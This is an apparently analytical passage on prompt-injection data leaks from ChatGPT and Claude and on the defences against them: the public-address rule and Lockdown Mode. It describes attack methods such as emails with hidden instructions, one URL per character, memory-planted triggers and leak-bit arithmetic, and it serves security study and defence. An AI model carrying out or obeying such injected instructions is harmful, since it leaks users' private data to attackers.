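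The October 2024 report proposed that ChatGPT ask the user before saving a memory and stop using tools automatically once a conversation contained untrusted text. Schwartzman likewise suggested asking the user before opening any link. He considered this a temporary solution and expected a game of "cat and mouse" as long as ChatGPT could open any address a user supplied.

OpenAI strengthened url_safe in the summer of 2025. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025), OpenAI told Tenable on 11 July that it had improved the check, in reply to a report about a different flaw. Rehberger dates the change that stopped his Black Hat attacks to around August, about ten months after he reported them. In his December slides, *Agentic ProbLLMs* (2025), he confirms that images from windows.net no longer got through. But in 2026 Embrace The Red still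 considered using one address per character a workable way to leak small amounts of data.

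## Allowing only web addresses that are already public

The web app's visible url_safe calls disappeared in mid-2025, which Rehberger, in Embrace The Red, took as a sign that OpenAI was changing the check. He had recommended running the check on OpenAI's servers, which would hide the calls from users, but he couldn't confirm that OpenAI had done this. In September, a researcher at the security company Radware found that OpenAI had also tightened the rules for ChatGPT's browsing tool, but that an attacker could still leak data without breaking the new rule.

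### ZombieAgent

Earlier attacks gave ChatGPT an address and told it to add private text to the end. According to Radware's *ZombieAgent*, OpenAI responded by restricting ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as provided, even when instructions told it to add something.

Zvika Babo, the Radware researcher, simply provided every address that the attack would need:

1. The attacker sends the user an email containing hidden instructions and 37 addresses, one for each letter and digit and one for a space.
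2. The user, who has connected ChatGPT to Gmail, asks it to do something with the inbox.
3. ChatGPT reads the email, follows the instructions, finds some private information and opens the addresses that spell it out.

Rehberger had tried one address per character with images in 2023. Babo mainly used the browsing tool, so the requests came from OpenAI's servers before the user saw any reply. He also tried markdown images but found them less reliable and easier to block. His results are therefore only weak evidence of how url_safe handled images by then.

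They do help answer whether text from someone other than the user could get an address approved, which the 2024 tests did not answer. Babo's addresses came from a stranger's email, and the browsing tool opened them.

Babo also dealt with requests that arrive out of order. He gave each character a separate address for each position in the text, so that a0 meant an "a" in the first position and a1 an "a" in the second. The attacker can then sort the requests by position. A block of ten characters needs 360 addresses to cover letters and digits.

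OpenAI had tried to stop attackers from making such a leak permanent. Once ChatGPT had used a connector such as Gmail, it couldn't use memory in the same chat, and it wouldn't open an attacker's addresses from a memory. Babo got around this by having ChatGPT read a memory first and use Gmail second, which OpenAI had not blocked. A shared file planted a memory telling ChatGPT to look up a certain email whenever the user wrote something, and that email contained the instructions.

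Babo reported the attack on 26 September 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that handles vulnerability reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd reproduced it four days later, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. Radware published the research on 8 January 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, but did not describe the fix.

### The public-address rule

On 28 January 2026 OpenAI published the kind of explanation that Rehberger had been requesting since 2023. It began by giving two reasons for rejecting a list of trusted sites. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so an address on a trusted domain can lead to an attacker's server, as it did in Tenable's attack through Bing. A strict list would also produce constant false alarms, because people visit far more than a few famous sites, and users who see too many warnings learn to click through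 them.

OpenAI's public-address rule ignores the reputation of the site and looks at the exact address:

1. A web crawler, a program that explores public pages much as a search engine does, records the addresses it finds. It has no access to conversations or accounts.
2. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or image automatically, OpenAI compares the full address with the crawler's records.
3. If the address matches one of them, ChatGPT loads it.
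4. If it doesn't, OpenAI either tells the model to try another website or shows the user a warning. The warning displays the address, explains that it may contain information from the conversation, and lets the user copy or open it.

The crawler found the address without access to any conversation, so the address can't have been composed from what this user told ChatGPT. It can't contain the user's secret unless the secret was already on the web or the match is a coincidence. OpenAI makes the slightly weaker claim that a public address is much less likely to contain private data.

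Compared with what researchers had found in 2024, the rule changes several answers:

| Address that ChatGPT wants to load | url_safe in 2024 | Public-address rule |
|---|---|---|
| An Azure image address with private text added | Safe | Not loaded automatically |
| A photo on a small blog that nobody has mentioned in the chat | Not safe | Loaded if the crawler has recorded it |
| A flashcard link that ChatGPT has composed | Not safe, so the link does nothing | Warning before the link opens |
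| `example.com/monday`, one of seven pages that an attacker published in advance | Not safe unless the address is in the conversation | Loaded if the crawler has recorded it |

The first row shows the main improvement. An attacker can still rent space on Azure, but no crawler will have seen an address that ChatGPT has just made up. The warning is also better for users than the dead links that GPT builders complained about. However, OpenAI's point about false alarms applies to its own rule too. When a website generates a report for one user, no crawler has seen the report's address, so people who use such services may see the warning often enough to stop reading it.

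OpenAI's post gives no starting date for the rule. Rehberger, in Embrace The Red, treats OpenAI's explanation as a description of the August 2025 changes. But if the rule had covered the browsing tool in September, Babo's list should have failed, unless the crawler had already recorded his addresses. Perhaps OpenAI applied the rule to images first.

### What a choice between public addresses reveals

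The last row of the table shows that the attacker can still learn the day of the dentist's appointment once the crawler has recorded all seven weekday pages. The page that ChatGPT opens reveals the day.

OpenAI acknowledges this problem in its technical paper on the rule, according to Embrace The Red. Rehberger adds that the owner of a larger website or blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. The attacker only has to tell the model which page stands for which character.

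The amount of information that can leak this way is usually measured in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. Choosing one of N equally likely addresses conveys log₂ N bits, which is 2.8 bits for a day of the week and 5.2 bits for one of 36 characters. The table gives the maximum leak for ten requests, the number of pages that ChatGPT would open per prompt in Schwartzman's tests.

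| What the attacker's log shows | Number of possible messages | Maximum leak |
|---|---|---|
| Order of requests, with repeats | 36¹⁰, about 3.7 quadrillion | 51.7 bits |
| Order of requests, each address at most once | 36 × 35 × … × 27, about 922 trillion | 49.7 bits |
| Only which ten addresses ChatGPT opened | The previous number divided by 10!, about 254 million | 27.9 bits |

A six-digit login code contains 19.9 bits, so it would fit in all three cases. A ten-digit phone number needs 33.2 bits and would fit only if the attacker could recover the order. The figures for the three cases are upper limits because they assume the model makes no mistakes. To get near the last figure, ChatGPT would also have to convert the secret into a set of ten pages, probably by running a program.

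Rehberger has proposed two further defences. ChatGPT could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it, or it could refuse to open the same address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker would see a request for each address at most once. Text with repeated characters would arrive incomplete, but the table shows that a well-prepared attacker would lose only two of 51.7 bits.

Babo's numbered addresses would recover even those two bits. If every position in the message has its own set of 36 addresses, ChatGPT never needs to open the same address twice, and the order of arrival no longer matters. The attacker needs 360 pages in the index instead of 36, which is more work but still feasible. Rehberger expected his proposals only to make the attack harder, and he had not checked whether ChatGPT already used them.

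Limiting the number of requests would help more. Allowing five requests instead of ten would halve the maximum to 25.8 bits. To compensate, the attacker would need far more pages, because doubling the number of pages adds only one bit per request. Rehberger suggests that an attacker could use thousands of addresses. With 4,096 addresses, each request would convey 12 bits, but the model would have to apply a very long code without errors.

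Even so, the public-address rule greatly reduced how much data an attacker could take per request. Leaking a random 128-bit key using 36 addresses would require 25 requests, whereas Zenity's Azure image sent API keys in a single request.

A leak from Anthropic's Claude in July 2026 shows that short secrets are worth the effort of stealing. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how Ayush Paul exploited Claude's tool for opening web pages. Anthropic let the tool open only exact addresses that the user had entered, that a search had returned, or that were linked from pages Claude had already opened. Paul used a website he had built to persuade Claude to spell out the user's details by following one link after another.

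The blogger dyb calculated in *The Read-Only Lie* that each page offered 27 links, so each choice of link conveyed 4.75 bits, and about 30 requests leaked roughly 143 bits. That was enough to convey Paul's name, employer and home city. Anthropic closed the gap by stopping the tool from following links on fetched pages. OpenAI's rule would have made Paul's version harder, because his site produced new addresses at every step and the crawler would have had to record them beforehand. The rule would not have stopped an attack that used a fixed set of 27 pages.

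### Tests of ChatGPT in 2026

Rehberger also warned in Embrace The Red that some OpenAI developers might not know about the protection and could ship a new feature without it. OpenAI had already done this with the macOS app. ChatGPT can also reach the internet without showing an image or opening a page. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (March 2026) describes one way to do this from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt could use it to leak messages and uploaded files.

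A test on 3 February 2026, six days after OpenAI's post, is harder to explain. Yang, Na and Choi (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection*, gave ChatGPT 5.2 a fictitious user's birthday and asked it to summarise a web page that contained hidden instructions. Their server logged three requests within five seconds. ChatGPT fetched the page, then a second page with text meant to overcome its safety training, and then an address whose query string contained `pageid=20050226`. The number is the user's birthday, 26 February 2005, disguised as a page ID.

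The public-address rule should have stopped that last request, unless the crawler happened to have recorded an address with the same number. Perhaps the rule did not yet cover every route to the browsing tool, or OpenAI made an exception that outsiders don't know about. Yang and colleagues did not investigate OpenAI's check, so their log doesn't show why the request went through. They report one successful leak but no success rate for the whole attack.

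The 72% success rate in their paper comes from a separate experiment on ChatGPT 5.3, which tested a new way of wording hidden instructions. The wording makes the conversation so far look like a worked example, which the model then continues with the attacker's task. It succeeded in 121 of 168 attempts, while an older technique succeeded in 4 of 136. Attempts did not have to get private data out of ChatGPT to count as successes. The experiments were in Korean and assumed that the attacker could predict the user's request. The researchers also noticed that small changes of tone affected the results.

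The security company Permiso tested images in the spring. In Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, a Firefox user asks ChatGPT to summarise a web page, and hidden text on the page makes ChatGPT add a picture to the summary. The picture loads automatically from storage that the researchers control. In another version, the picture's address belongs to a link-shortening service that redirects the request to the researchers' server.

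The request to the server revealed the user's IP address (which identifies their internet connection), browser type, and when ChatGPT produced the answer. An attacker could use this to confirm that a particular person had read a particular page. The picture could also be a QR code leading to a phishing site, which the user would open on a phone that the computer's security software doesn't protect.

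No text from the conversation leaked. The image address was the same for every reader and was already on the page, so Permiso's result doesn't contradict the argument for the public-address rule. Permiso did not test whether a page could offer several images and get ChatGPT to pick one based on a secret.

Permiso reported the flaw to OpenAI on 29 April 2026. A day later, OpenAI marked the report "Not Reproducible" because it lacked detail. The report's title had also claimed that the flaw allowed cross-site scripting, which would let an attacker run code in the user's ChatGPT session. The published research does not show this. Permiso sent a revised version on 1 May with more steps and without that claim. OpenAI first classified it as "Not Applicable" and later as a duplicate of an earlier report. Permiso followed up on 7 May and published its research on 29 May.

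### Lockdown Mode

Users who want stricter protection can turn on Lockdown Mode. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it for organisations on 13 February, and OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts on 4 June. OpenAI intended it for people such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and considers it unnecessary for most users.

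The mode prevents most of the requests that an attacker could observe. When browsing, ChatGPT can read only copies of pages that OpenAI has already stored, and no live request leaves OpenAI's network. This closes the gap in the public-address rule. Hidden instructions could still make ChatGPT choose the page for Monday, but ChatGPT would read OpenAI's copy, and the owner of example.com would not learn which page it chose. Rehberger's idea of reusing pages for a few minutes would also reduce the requests an attacker can observe, but the first visit would still reach the attacker.

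According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, a help page current in early December 2026, ChatGPT may also stop showing images in ordinary replies and stop fetching them from the web. Users can still upload images and generate new ones.

The mode makes ChatGPT much less useful. Search results may be old or missing. Deep research, which produces long reports from many web sources, doesn't work, and neither does agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites. ChatGPT can't download files to analyse them, and users can't let code written in its Canvas editor connect to the internet. On personal accounts, the mode also blocks live access to outside services and changes to data in connected apps where these conflict with its protections. A user who needs one of these features can turn the mode off for a single chat.

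Lockdown Mode leaves some routes for data leaks open. In workspaces run by an organisation, administrators decide which apps remain available. OpenAI advises them not to let an app write anything where an attacker might see it. Otherwise, ChatGPT could put a secret in a shared document, much as Rehberger made it do with plugins in 2023, and rules about image addresses would not prevent the leak. Lockdown Mode also leaves memory switched on and does not restrict internet access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

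OpenAI does not promise that the mode will prevent every leak, citing the apps that remain enabled, unforeseen combinations of features, and undiscovered techniques. Hidden instructions can still reach the model through a stored page or an uploaded file and make it give a wrong answer.

Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomed the mode because it relies on fixed restrictions instead of having each request judged by an AI model, which an attacker might fool. He also took the mode's existence to imply that ChatGPT's normal settings don't protect robustly against a determined attacker. The arithmetic above supports that inference, since the public-address rule lets small leaks through even when it works perfectly.

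Researchers at Check Point also found a flaw in Lockdown Mode. ChatGPT can preview web pages it has written, and it runs the preview in a sandbox, an enclosed part of the app that can't contact other servers without the user's consent. A previewed page could open a pop-up window outside the sandbox, where the restrictions didn't apply. An attacker could deliver such a page through a crafted prompt, a malicious GPT or a shared chat, and use it to steal messages. In the desktop app this required no click, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026). OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026, about three months after it started offering Lockdown Mode to personal accounts.
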